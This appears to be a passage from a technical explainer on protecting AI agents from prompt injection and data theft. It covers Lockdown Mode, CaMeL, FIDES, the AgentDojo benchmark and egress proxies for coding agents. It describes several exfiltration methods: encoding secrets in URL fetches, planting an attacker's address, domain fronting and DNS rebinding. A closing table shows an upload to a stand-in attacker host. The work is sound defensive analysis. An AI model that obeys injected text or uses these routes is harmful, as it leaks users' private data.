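| 65,536 | 16 | 16 |

Doubling the number of pages adds only one bit per fetch. To send the whole key in one request, as the image attacks of 2023 could, the attacker would need 2²⁵⁶ pages in the index, which is impossible. The check therefore makes the theft of a key much slower and more conspicuous. It does little to protect short secrets. Whether a company is planning a merger is one bit, and a six-digit login code is just under 20 bits, which the attacker can send in three fetches by choosing among 256 addresses each time.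 The bound counts only the choice of address, but the timing of the requests can carry extra information, as in Lampson's covert channels.

Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large website probably already has 36 suitable pages in the index, and that an attacker could go on to use thousands. Tenable had used a similar method against url_safe in 2025. url_safe always approved Bing's domain, and Bing gives each search result a fixed link that redirects to the site. Tenable got one page per letter into Bing's results and used each page's link to represent its letter.

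Rehberger suggested two further restrictions. OpenAI could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it if the agent requested the page again, so that the attacker's server would not receive the second request. Or it could prevent an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. He had noticed in 2023 that browsers already hindered this kind of attack slightly, because they cache pages and their requests can arrive out of order. He had not tested whether OpenAI had adopted either idea.

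Both would hurt an attacker with few pages much more than one with many. If the agent can open each of 36 addresses only once, there are about 2¹³⁹·⁵ possible sequences of any length, so a session can carry just under 140 bits, too few for the 256-bit key. If the order is also lost, the attacker can tell only which addresses the agent opened, and the limit drops to 36 bits. But with 256 addresses and a reliable order, a ban on repeats raises the minimum number of fetches for the key only from 32 to 33. An attacker who can't rely on the order could copy Radware's method and prepare 256 addresses for each of the key's 32 bytes. That takes 8,192 indexed pages, but the agent never has to open the same one twice.

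There is little public evidence on how well ChatGPT's protections work together. *The Framing Gap* (2026) reports that attacks that succeeded up to 100% of the time against a model reached through OpenAI's API failed in all 48 valid trials against ChatGPT. The researchers could not see inside the product, so they did not credit the address check or any other single defence. Zero successes in 48 independent trials would be consistent with a true success rate of up to about 6%.

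### Lockdown Mode

On February 13, 2026, OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode, a stricter option for people who handle especially sensitive data (*Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, 2026). OpenAI offered it first to organisations, including businesses, schools and healthcare providers. On June 4 it began extending the option to personal accounts and to small businesses that manage their own subscriptions.

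In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT can browse only cached pages (copies OpenAI already holds), so no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network. This also blocks the alphabet attacks, because the attacker's server receives no record of which stored copies the agent opens. The mode switches off Deep Research and agent mode. ChatGPT can't download files for analysis or retrieve images from the web, and it might not display images in ordinary answers. Users can't give network access to code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace.

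Lockdown Mode makes ChatGPT less useful. OpenAI's help page for the feature, *Lockdown Mode*, warns that search results may be limited, out of date or missing. Personal accounts also lose the finance and shopping features, as well as live access to outside services where it conflicts with the protections. Users can still upload files and generate images, and ChatGPT's memory works as before. Personal account users who need a blocked feature can turn the mode off for a single chat, but that chat then loses the protection.

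Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, approved of the design because it uses fixed rules to cut off the means of sending data, rather than relying on an AI model that an attacker might fool. He also concluded that ChatGPT's default settings do not offer robust protection against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's head of information security, said the mode was not meant for everyone but was a worthwhile tradeoff for people at higher risk because of who they are or what they work on.

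OpenAI does not guarantee that Lockdown Mode will prevent every leak. Its help page lists three remaining risks: apps that stay connected, unforeseen combinations of features, and new techniques. Prompt injections can still reach the model through a cached page or an uploaded file and make its answers wrong. The mode has no effect on network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

Connected apps are the largest gap for organisations, because Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically disable them in managed workspaces, where an administrator chooses which apps and actions remain available. OpenAI advises against enabling any action that writes data, even in a trusted app, unless the administrator is confident that an attacker can't see the result. Creating a private calendar entry might meet that condition, but commenting on a public software project would not. However, the administrator makes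 this choice once for each action, before anyone knows what the agent will write. For example, permission to post to a company-wide channel would let the agent post a list of salaries as well as a lunch menu.

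## 2025: labels that follow data through an agent

Confidentiality labels let software distinguish a salary list from a lunch menu when an agent posts either one, but only if the salary file's label carries over to whatever the agent writes after reading the file. The system can follow a value from one variable to the next in an ordinary program, but tracking data through a language model is harder because the model receives its input as one text and nobody can say for certain which parts shaped the output. Two systems from 2025, CaMeL from Google DeepMind and FIDES from Microsoft, keep most of the data away from the model that makes the decisions. Both build on a proposal Willison made two years earlier.

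### Two models and a controller

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) asked what kind of assistant developers could safely build if nobody found a cure for prompt injection. His design has three components:

- The privileged model takes requests from the user and decides which tools to run. It never sees text from untrusted sources.
- The quarantined model reads untrusted text, such as emails and web pages. It has no tools, so an injection can't make it act.
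- The controller, an ordinary program, runs the tools and passes data between the two models.

The controller stores untrusted text in variables and gives the privileged model only their names. Suppose the user wants a summary of the latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores the text as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller puts the email into a prompt for the quarantined model, stores the output as `$VAR2` and reports only that the summary is ready. The privileged model then has the controller display `$VAR2` to the user. An instruction hidden in the email may spoil the summary, but it never reaches the privileged model, which can send mail.

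Willison allowed one exception. If the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of categories, the controller can check that the answer is on the list and then show it to the privileged model, because a category name has no room for an injected instruction.

Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes the software more complicated, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text through to the privileged model undoes the protection. The quarantined model's output can also trick the user. He imagined an answer with instructions to paste a block of Base64 into a website to get a funny picture, when the block contains the user's private data.

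### A program written before the data arrives

The Dual LLM design protects the choice of tools but not the values passed to them. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits Google DeepMind's paper *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* with identifying this flaw. In the DeepMind paper's example, a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting. The meeting notes contain the document's name and Bob's email address. The privileged model can't read the notes, so the quarantined model extracts the address. If an attacker has tampered with the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address, and the agent then follows the steps the user wanted but sends the document to the attacker.

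CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in that paper, adds a record of where each value came from. The privileged model first turns the user's request into a complete program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's document, the program might look like this:

```
notes   = find_notes("last meeting")
name    = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
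file    = fetch_document(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=file)
```

A custom interpreter runs the program step by step. It tags each value with its sources and who may read it. A new value inherits the tags of the values used to compute it, so `address` inherits the tags of `notes`. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies that tool's policy. Reading the notes might always be allowed, while sending an email might require an address that the user already trusts. The interpreter can ask the user to approve an unknown address, such as one planted by an attacker, before any document is sent.

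CaMeL's tags are called "capabilities", but they describe a value, whereas Hardy's capabilities carry the right to use an object. The tags are closer to Denning's labels but allow more flexible policies. Girrens and Wang note that CaMeL can express rules that a simple comparison of two labels cannot, but that its security then depends on every tool's policy being correct. The CaMeL paper acknowledges that users have to write and maintain these policies, and that frequent approval requests may wear them down.

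Writing the program first can also help protect privacy. The quarantined model's task is easier, so a small model on the user's own computer could do it. The company that hosts the privileged model would then see only the user's request, not the private data.

It also makes some work harder. The program has to process each tool's output before any model has seen it, so the privileged model must know the output's exact format. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL needed full descriptions of these formats to achieve reasonable results on two benchmarks, and treats writing them as a modest one-time job for developers. A more basic difficulty is that the next step sometimes depends on the content of the data. For example, nobody can turn "do the jobs on my to-do list" into a fixed program without reading the list.

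The privileged model sometimes writes code that gets around this difficulty but defeats the design. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) gave CaMeL a task that required reading a file and following the instructions in it, with policy checks off. The model wrote a loop that translated each instruction into a tool call. Whoever wrote the file could then control the agent, and two attacks succeeded this way.

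Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's tracking has the same flaw that Fenton's small program exposed in the 1970s. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when an assignment runs, so a program can reveal a secret through an assignment that it skips. In their example, a variable labelled public reveals whether a bank balance exceeds a threshold, and the program can email that answer to anyone. A second leak arises because CaMeL doesn't track the loop that reruns a program after a failure. An attempt can reveal one bit by whether the policy blocks it, and repeated attempts can extract a whole secret. Both leaks should be hard for an outsider to exploit, because the privileged model writes its program without reading the outsider's text, but they matter more if that model misbehaves.

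### The AgentDojo benchmark

Researchers have tested both systems on AgentDojo, a set of simulated workplaces and accounts. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, wrote 97 tasks for users and 27 goals for attackers, then paired every task with every attacker's goal in the same setting:

| Setting | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (mail, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 |
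| Slack (workplace chat, web pages) | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

In one banking pair, the user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a file, while the attacker wants it to send as much money as possible to another account. The benchmark places the attacker's text in data that the agent reads during the task. Ordinary code then inspects the agent's answer and the state of the simulated accounts. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that works on the agent might also work on the judge.

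The code produces three scores: the share of tasks the agent completes without an attack, the share it completes correctly under attack, and the share of attacks that succeed. In 2024, the tested models completed fewer than 66% of the tasks even without an attack. Attacks succeeded in fewer than 25% of cases against the best agents, and a separate injection detector reduced this to 8%. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, because weaker ones often failed at the attacker's task as well as the user's.

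### CaMeL's results

The CaMeL paper describes the system as having effectively solved AgentDojo. Later reruns by other researchers support the security claim, but CaMeL failed many of the tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran CaMeL's released code on the whole benchmark, through an adapter. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. The adapter may have caused some of those failures.

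Two reruns, each on a single setting, measured how the policy checks affect CaMeL's task completion. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL completed 37.5% of banking runs with the checks on, about half its rate with them off. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, ran CaMeL with four recent models on the 21 Slack tasks. It completed 13 to 17 of them with the checks off and 4 to 6 with them on. The checks therefore still reduce completion with better models. Many of these tasks ask the agent to act on information from a source the policy does not trust.

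The checks also provide only part of CaMeL's security. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 banking pairs, the attack needed a tool call that would never appear in a program for the user's task. For example, a program that only summarises recent transactions has no payment step, so an attacker cannot use it to send money. In the other 47 pairs, the program might contain a call that suits the attacker, so stopping the attack depends on the labels.

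CaMeL's original evaluation counted two injections as successful, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the user asked the agent to make whatever payment a document described, and the attacker had changed the document. Labels can show that the document is untrusted but can't distinguish a false bill from a real one, and CaMeL's creators had placed this case outside their threat model. The other was a scoring error. The agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark counted the attacker's phrase in the quotation as a successful attack.

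CaMeL also uses more computing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, on the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent. Tokens are the pieces of text that a model reads and writes, and providers usually charge by the token.

### FIDES: labels inside the agent loop

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, which keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the model receives the result of each step before choosing the next. FIDES gives every message, tool result and tool argument two labels. The integrity label is T for trusted or U for untrusted, and the confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the data. The user's request and the developer's standing instructions normally start as (T, everyone).

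Combining two pieces of data joins both parts of the pair. The result is trusted only if both inputs are, and its readers are the people on both lists:

(T, {A, B}) ⊕ (U, {B, C}) = (U, {B})

The same rule applies to the model's output. FIDES cannot tell which parts of the context influenced it, so the output inherits the join of all the labels in the context. If one message out of fifty came from a stranger, everything the model writes afterwards is labelled untrusted, including sentences unrelated to that message. Other researchers have tried to identify the messages that influenced an answer and regenerate it from those alone, which can give it a less restrictive label. Costa and colleagues left this out to keep the system simple.

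Before each tool call, ordinary code compares the labels with a policy for that tool. FIDES has two basic policies:

- A consequential call, such as a payment, may run only if the decision to make it and all its arguments are trusted.
- A call that sends data may run only if every reader of the channel is among the data's permitted readers. The readers of an email are its recipients, and those of a group chat are its members.

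The reader policy limits the damage from prompt injection but does not prevent it. An attacker could still make the agent send an email, but only to people who may already see its contents. Applying only the first policy to a sending tool lets trusted decisions override the reader lists, which is a form of declassification. Costa and colleagues reason that if no untrusted text could have influenced the decision, the disclosure was intentional. This is reasonable for attacks, but a model can also misunderstand a trustworthy request and send a file to the wrong colleague.

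The benchmark tests used adapted versions of both policies. The first checked only whether the decision was trusted and ignored the arguments. The second also refused any message that contained an untrusted link, because a web address can carry data out. Email and several other sending tools could run if they satisfied either policy.

### Hidden variables

Under these rules alone, an agent would lose many of its powers as soon as it read an email from a stranger. FIDES avoids this by hiding data that would change the context's label. The loop works as follows:

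1. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the label of each field with the label of the context.
2. If a field would leave the context's label unchanged, FIDES adds its text to the context. Otherwise, it stores the text and label in memory and shows the model only a variable name.
3. The model chooses its next step. It can use variable names as arguments without seeing what they contain.
4. FIDES replaces each name with the stored value and label, then checks the policy.
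5. If the call passes, the tool runs, and its result inherits the labels of the call, the arguments and any data that the tool reads. If the call fails, the model receives an error and can try another approach.

The model might therefore see an email's timestamp but not its body. Because each argument keeps its own label, a trusted decision can include untrusted data. For example, a policy could require a trusted recipient but accept a message body taken from the web.

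Two tools let the agent use what a variable contains. One sends the variable to an isolated model with no tools and stores the answer in a new variable. The other reveals the contents to the planner, the part of the agent that chooses the steps. The planner can then react to the text, but its context takes on the variable's label for the rest of the session. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) contrasts this choice with CaMeL, where the plan can't depend on what the tools return.

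### The same request with and without FIDES

Suppose Ana tells her agent, "summarise my emails and send the summary to my manager". The agent's standing instructions give the address of her manager, Ben, so the address is trusted. Ana has two emails. One is a progress report that Carla, a colleague, sent to Ana and Ben. The other is from a stranger, was sent only to Ana, and contains an instruction to forward the top email in her mailbox to the stranger's address. As in the benchmark, the permitted readers of an email are its sender and recipients, and its body is untrusted.

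A basic planner puts both emails straight into the context:

| Step | Label of the new item | Label of the context |
|---|---|---|
| Ana makes her request | (T, everyone) | (T, everyone) |
| The planner calls the mail-reading tool | (T, everyone) | (T, everyone) |
| Carla's email arrives | (U, {Ana, Ben, Carla}) | (U, {Ana, Ben, Carla}) |
| The stranger's email arrives | (U, {Ana, stranger}) | (U, {Ana}) |
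| The planner writes a summary and tries to send it to Ben | (U, {Ana}) | (U, {Ana}) |

The policy blocks the last step because Ben is not permitted to read the summary and the planner made the decision in an untrusted context. An attempt to forward Carla's report to the stranger would fail for the same reasons. The labels stop the attack, but they also stop Ana's task, and would have stopped it even if the stranger had written only to advertise a conference.

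FIDES stores the bodies as variables:

| Step | Label of the new item | Label of the context |
|---|---|---|
| Ana makes her request | (T, everyone) | (T, everyone) |
| The planner calls the mail-reading tool | (T, everyone) | (T, everyone) |
| FIDES stores Carla's email as V1 | (U, {Ana, Ben, Carla}) | (T, everyone) |
| FIDES stores the stranger's email as V2 | (U, {Ana, stranger}) | (T, everyone) |
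| The isolated model summarises V1 and V2, and FIDES stores the result as V3 | (U, {Ana}) | (T, everyone) |
| The planner asks to send V3 to Ben | decision and address: (T, everyone); body: (U, {Ana}) | (T, everyone) |

The summary still fails the reader policy because Ben never received the stranger's email. But the decision to send it is trusted, since the planner was given only Ana's request and the variable names. The benchmark's email rule requires only one policy to pass, so the summary goes to Ben.

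The stranger can still affect what Ben reads. The isolated model might follow the injected text and write an empty or false summary. It might also add a link whose address contains text from Carla's report. The reader policy blocks messages with untrusted links, but the trusted decision overrides that block too. As the rule is written, the email would go out and Ben could leak the text by clicking the link. Requiring both policies to pass would prevent this leak, but it would also block the summary Ana asked for.

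### Limiting the isolated model's answers

Some tasks require the planner to use information from hidden data. If Ana asks the agent to create a calendar entry for any meeting that an email proposes, the planner's next step depends on whether the email proposes one. Without reading the email, the planner can have the isolated model produce a yes or no and reveal that answer to itself. If the answer is yes, it can have the isolated model extract the date and names into another hidden variable for the calendar tool.

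The planner specifies the format of the answer in advance. A technique called constrained decoding then prevents the isolated model from producing anything else. FIDES orders these formats by how much information they can carry:

yes or no → a choice from a fixed list → free text

A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, a choice from a list carries more as the list grows, and free text has no fixed limit. FIDES adds the answer's format to its security label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no where it would refuse an untrusted paragraph. Software can then apply Willison's exception for fixed categories as a rule for any tool.

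An attacker can't fit a new instruction into one bit but can still choose the bit's value, for example by making the isolated model report a meeting that nobody proposed. Bits also add up over many questions, as they did over many web requests, even if each answer looks harmless when checked separately. Garby and colleagues object that a reviewer who looks at a single run can't tell whether such an answer was an intended exception or a leak. The benchmark results don't show how much this matters, because Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their tests, and most AgentDojo tasks did not need it.

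### Explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues proved that their label-tracking loop can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. The property concerns two versions of a company's data, *d₁* and *d₂*, that differ only in their secrets, so an outsider can't tell them apart. The agent runs on *d₁* and makes a series of tool calls, whose combined effect is a function *g*. Explicit secrecy requires that *g*(*d₁*) and *g*(*d₂*) also look the same to the outsider. A call that copied a secret into a public file would violate the property, because the outsider could then see a difference between the two results.

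The definition applies the same calls to both versions of the data, although the agent might have made different calls if the secret had been different. Explicit secrecy therefore permits Denning's implicit flows. For example, an agent can send "good morning" only if a contract mentions a merger, because the message contains nothing from the contract. The attacks that spelled out secrets through a choice of web addresses relied on the same kind of inference. The guarantee also does not cover timing or the size of network packets.

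A stronger property, non-interference, would require everything an outsider can observe to stay the same whatever the secrets are. Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive, because an agent that had called any tool capable of reading secrets could not then call one that might write somewhere public. Ana's agent, for example, could not reply to a customer after opening one confidential file, even if she dictated the reply. Phone-monitoring software and web browsers also enforce something weaker than non-interference.

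Garby and colleagues argue that explicit secrecy is weakest in systems where data can easily become instructions, because the agent's choices can then leak data efficiently. They proved a form of non-interference for their own agent language, although the proof doesn't cover information revealed by whether a program finishes. CaMeL came with no comparable proof.

The proof for FIDES also assumes that the model always gives the same output for the same input, and that the user's messages, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions can be trusted. Above all, it assumes that the labels are correct. Costa and colleagues inferred an email's readers from its address lines, but acknowledged that people may have shared it more widely.

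### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with two OpenAI models from 2024, GPT-4o and the reasoning model o1, and averaged all results over five runs. For the security tests, they used an attack that names the agent's own tools and had worked well against GPT-4o.

With policy checks off, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES. The best probabilistic defence tested, which asks the model to discard unneeded tools at the start, let 20 attacks through, so hiding data alone was about as effective. With the checks on, no attack succeeded against either planner. AgentDojo's scoring still recorded three successes against FIDES, but the researchers rejected them after reading the runs. For example, the benchmark counts some attacks as successful even when a policy has blocked the call, and others when the agent does something the policy permits.

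The labels in this test were unusually favourable to the defence. AgentDojo doesn't supply labels, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This meant that no attack could arrive in a field marked trusted. A company labelling its own data would not know in advance which fields attackers will use.

The effect on ordinary work depended heavily on the model. These figures are the average percentage of tasks completed without an attack, giving the four settings equal weight:

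| Planner | GPT-4o, checks off | GPT-4o, checks on | o1, checks off | o1, checks on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 84.3 | 41.9 | 84.0 | 44.4 |
| FIDES | 60.6 | 50.0 | 77.6 | 60.8 |

With the checks on, FIDES's task completion rate was 8 percentage points higher than the basic planner's with GPT-4o and 16 points higher with o1. With the checks off, hiding data lowered FIDES's completion rate by 6.3 points with o1 and 23.7 with GPT-4o, which often confused variable names or failed to use the isolated model when it should have. Compared with an agent with no protection, FIDES with its checks on had a completion rate about 23 points lower with o1 and 34 points lower with GPT-4o.

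Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom built FIDES, consider that last comparison unfair because an unprotected agent scores as if a person had approved everything it did, while the protected agent gets no approvals. Many real products already ask for approval before taking a consequential action. Labels could reduce the number of requests in those products, because the agent would need to ask only when a policy check fails.

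The averages also hide large differences between settings. With GPT-4o and the checks on, FIDES raised the completion rate on Slack tasks from 20% to 47.6%, but lowered it on travel tasks from 73% to 41%. Many travel tools could run in an untrusted context as long as no private data leaked, so the basic planner lost little there. With o1, FIDES reached 68% on travel tasks, compared with 75% for the basic planner.

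Costa and colleagues classified the tasks by how much information the planner needs. In about a quarter of them, the planner can pass hidden data from one tool to another. About half also need the isolated model, as Ana's summary does. In the remaining fifth, mostly banking and Slack tasks, the right steps depend on the data itself. Many of the banking failures were deliberate refusals, because the user had asked the agent to follow the instructions in an untrusted file.

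Some successes were lucky. One task asked the agent to change the user's password if a suspicious payment appeared. GPT-4o had access to the amounts but not the hidden descriptions, so it treated a large payment as suspicious and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because the amounts were trusted, and AgentDojo counted the task as complete.

FIDES can also use many tokens, because it sends the growing history back to the planner at every step. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapted FIDES and CaMeL to agents that operate a computer screen. The FIDES version's token overhead was 29.6 times the undefended agent's use, compared with 1.88 times for the CaMeL version, which plans only once. Costa and colleagues had not tried to make FIDES efficient, but they suggested grouping questions to the isolated model and running several tool calls together.

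AgentDojo's standard attacks are also outdated. In the 2026 tests by Zhou and colleagues, all 105 Slack injections failed against Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT 5.4 and Sonnet 5, even with CaMeL's policy checks off. To simulate stronger attacks, the researchers modified their own system so that the part of the agent reading an injection had to follow it. Between 16% and 42% of the attacks then succeeded without label checks, depending on the model, and none succeeded with the checks on.

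## October 2025: coding agents behind a default-deny proxy

CaMeL and FIDES check each tool call against a policy, but a coding agent also has a shell, which runs any command or program the model writes. If the agent program blocks `curl`, which sends web requests, the model can put the same request in a script and run `python fix.py`. NVIDIA warns that attackers often get past allowlists this way, using an approved tool to call a restricted one.

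During 2025, several companies put network limits outside their coding agents, so the limits also apply to scripts the agents start. OpenAI kept Codex offline by default and let users permit a list of domains, an approach Willison called sensible in June. In July, GitHub (2025) let developers adjust the firewall around its Copilot coding agent. On October 20, Anthropic released an open-source sandbox for Claude Code and explained its design in *Beyond permission prompts* (2025).

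### Fewer permission prompts

Claude Code originally read files freely but asked the user before changing a file, running most commands or using the network. Users accepted 93% of these prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, and a later figure is 97%. Most prompts concern harmless commands, so a high approval rate does not prove carelessness. But users reject 39% of Claude's proposed plans, which suggests that they read plans more closely than single commands. Anthropic also found that by June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule approving some shell commands in advance, and a quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips the prompts.

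With the sandbox, the user sets the limits once, and commands inside them run without a prompt. In Anthropic's internal use, this cut the number of prompts by 84%. That figure doesn't measure how many leaks the sandbox prevented, but the reduction matters for security because the remaining prompts should mostly concern something outside the limits, which gives the user more reason to read them.

### Making the proxy the only way out

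An egress proxy can enforce an allowlist only if programs in the sandbox have no other route to the network. In *How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy*, the engineering blogger simedw describes two attempts that left other routes open.

The first used environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, which set the proxy that programs should send their traffic through. Most tools use these settings, but a script that opens its own connection can bypass them. The second used an internal network in Docker, a system for running programs in containers. This removed the normal route to the internet, but Docker's name server still answered queries. The container could also reach services on the host machine, and traffic using IPv6, the newer internet addressing system, needed separate rules.

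Claude Code's sandbox closes these routes as follows, according to Anthropic:

1. **Remove the network.** On Linux, each command runs in a separate network namespace, a private set of network connections that in this case has no link to the real network. On a Mac, Apple's Seatbelt framework blocks connections to anything except the proxy.
2. **Leave one opening.** On Linux, a Unix socket, which connects programs on the same machine, links the sandbox to a proxy outside it. Environment variables direct ordinary tools to the proxy. A program that ignores them can't connect at all.
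3. **Check the name.** The program gives the proxy a hostname, and the proxy compares it with the lists of allowed and denied domains. The allowed list starts empty.
4. **Look up the address.** The proxy does this only after the name has passed, because a lookup can itself carry data out. It refuses the connection if the name leads only to local addresses, such as those of the user's own machine.
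5. **Connect or refuse.** If the host is not on the list, the proxy waits for a decision from the user or a classifier, or refuses immediately under a strict setting. The command's result names the refused host, so the agent knows what went wrong.

The address check in step 4 prevents a permitted name from resolving to a dangerous address. On Amazon's cloud, for example, a program can request temporary credentials from 169.254.169.254, and an attacker who controls a permitted name can point it there. The attacker can also try DNS rebinding, in which their name server gives a harmless address for the check and a different one for the connection. simedw's proxy prevents this by connecting to the address it checked. Codex makes a similar check, but OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* says this reduces the risk of rebinding without eliminating it.

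simedw's own solution keeps the container's network but puts a firewall around it. The firewall accepts traffic to one destination, the proxy's address and port. It drops the protocols that carry ordinary name lookups and `ping` messages, and the setup turns off IPv6. The proxy variables remain, but only for convenience.

These restrictions also break some legitimate tools. In Claude Code's sandbox, most database drivers and the plain `ssh` command can't connect even to a permitted host, because they don't use the proxy. Docker doesn't work there either. A developer who needs such a tool has to run it outside the sandbox, where the file and network limits don't apply.

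### File limits and network limits

Anthropic argues that a sandbox needs to restrict both files and network traffic. Without network limits, an agent that can read the developer's SSH keys can send them to an outside server. If the sandbox restricts only network traffic, the agent can still get a program outside the sandbox to send the keys. For example, it could add a command to the shell's start-up file. The next time the developer opens a terminal, that command runs with the developer's full access and no proxy.

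Claude Code therefore blocks sandboxed commands from writing outside the project and a few other directories. Even inside the project, they can't change shell start-up files or Claude Code's own settings, because doing so could give them wider access. But they can read almost the whole computer, including files that hold credentials, unless the user blocks access. This makes the network limits especially important in the default setup.

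The sandbox covers only shell commands and the processes they start. Claude's own file and web tools run outside it under separate permission rules, and local tool servers run with the user's full access. An attacker who can't send data out with a script may still be able to use one of those tools. A developer can cover them by running all of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine. Anthropic describes a container with no network, connected to an outside proxy by a single socket.

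### Claude Code, Codex and Copilot

The three companies set different defaults for what an agent can reach. The table compares Claude Code's local sandbox with two cloud services, using Anthropic's documentation, OpenAI's *Agent internet access* and GitHub's firewall guide.

| | Claude Code sandbox | Codex cloud | Copilot cloud agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Default | Sandbox off; empty list once the user turns it on | No internet access while the agent works | Firewall on, with a recommended list of hosts |
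| Basis for rules | Hostname and, optionally, port | Domain and type of request | Domain, or web address down to a path |
| Adding a host | User, administrator or classifier | Settings for each environment | Repository or organisation administrator |
| Outside the limits | Claude's own web and file tools, tool servers | Setup scripts | Tool servers, setup steps |

OpenAI illustrates the danger with an issue much like issue 212, in which someone reports that a script causes an error and asks the agent to run it. The script sends the project's latest code change to an outside website. It fails if internet access is off or limited to OpenAI's preset list of 71 common development domains, which doesn't include that website.

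GitHub's default is more convenient because the agent can download software packages immediately, but it gives an attacker more permitted services to try. GitHub warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass its firewall and that customers should not treat it as a complete security solution.

### What a rule can see

A filter can apply only the rules that its view of the traffic supports:

| The filter sees | Possible rule | What it misses |
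|---|---|---|
| IP address and port | Allow one address on port 443 | Which of several sites at that address receives the data |
| Hostname | Allow `api.github.com` | Whether the agent is reading or writing, and in whose account |
| Method and path | Allow comments on one project's issues | What a comment contains |
| Request body | Refuse a comment containing a known token | The same token in an encoding that the rule doesn't recognise |

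Most web traffic is encrypted with TLS between the program and the website. To reach a secure site through a proxy, a program first sends the proxy the site's hostname, for example with `CONNECT api.github.com:443`. The proxy then opens a connection and passes encrypted data in both directions. It can read the hostname in the `CONNECT` request, but not the method (such as `GET` or `POST`) or URL path of the encrypted requests that follow.

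A program in the sandbox can bypass the allowlist through domain fronting. Many websites share the servers of a content delivery network. The program can name a permitted site to the proxy, then name another site on the same network inside the encrypted request. If the network forwards the request to the second site, the data goes to a host that isn't on the list. Anthropic warns that its default proxy may be vulnerable to this because it trusts the name the program supplies.

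### The price of decryption

A proxy can see the rest of the request if it terminates TLS, which means decrypting the traffic and encrypting it again for the website. It can then compare the name inside the request with the one the program gave at the start. It can also add a credential to the request, so the agent never has to hold it.

A program normally checks that a website's certificate comes from a certificate authority the program trusts, so that nobody between them can pose as the website. A decrypting proxy has to pose as the website, so its operator creates a private certificate authority, installs it as trusted in the sandbox, and lets the proxy issue a certificate for each site the agent visits.

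Programs look for trusted authorities in different places, so simedw sets five environment variables to cover the common tools. If one is missing, some program will reject the proxy's certificate, and the agent may respond by turning off certificate checks. The proxy would still control the traffic, but the agent might also leave checks turned off in the code it is writing, which would make the finished product less secure. Some programs accept only certain certificates, a practice called pinning, and may not work through the proxy whatever the settings are.

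The operator also has to guard the authority's private key. Anyone who steals it can impersonate any website to a machine that trusts the authority, so the key should stay outside the sandbox and developers should not install the authority on their ordinary computers. The proxy also becomes a valuable target because passwords, private code and messages pass through it in readable form. Anthropic reports that its established isolation software has been dependable, but that an allowlist proxy it built in-house failed.

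Claude Code's built-in proxy doesn't decrypt traffic by default. An experimental setting lets it decrypt traffic to substitute credentials, but doesn't add rules about content. A developer who wants such rules has to supply a separate proxy, which must then do all the filtering for the traffic it receives.

Codex cloud can limit requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the methods that normally retrieve information. According to the documentation republished in *zerobox-network-proxy 0.3.1*, Codex's proxy must decrypt HTTPS traffic to enforce this limit, and blocks the traffic if it can't. The method is only a rough guide to what a request does. A GET request can carry secrets in its URL, as the image attacks did, and downloading a repository with Git over HTTPS normally requires a POST request.

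### Five requests from the issue-reading agent

Suppose the company's public project is `acme/app` and one of its private repositories is `acme/billing`. The agent has to read the public project and comment on its issues. A simple allowlist would permit `api.github.com` and refuse every other host. A decrypting proxy could enforce narrower rules:

- Allow GET requests to `api.github.com` for paths under `/repos/acme/app/`.
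- Allow POST requests to `api.github.com` for comments on that project's issues.
- Refuse everything else.

| Request | Hostname list | Method and path rules |
|---|---|---|
| Read issue 212: `GET api.github.com/repos/acme/app/issues/212` | Allow | Allow |
| Post a diagnosis: `POST api.github.com/repos/acme/app/issues/212/comments` | Allow | Allow |
| Read private code: `GET api.github.com/repos/acme/billing/contents/config` | Allow | Refuse |
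| Publish a file elsewhere on GitHub: `POST api.github.com/gists` | Allow | Refuse |
| Upload to the attacker: `POST collector.example/upload` | Refuse | Refuse |

The hostname list stops only the upload to the attacker's server. The narrower rules also keep the agent from accessing the private repository, even though its token allows access, and from publishing files elsewhere on GitHub.

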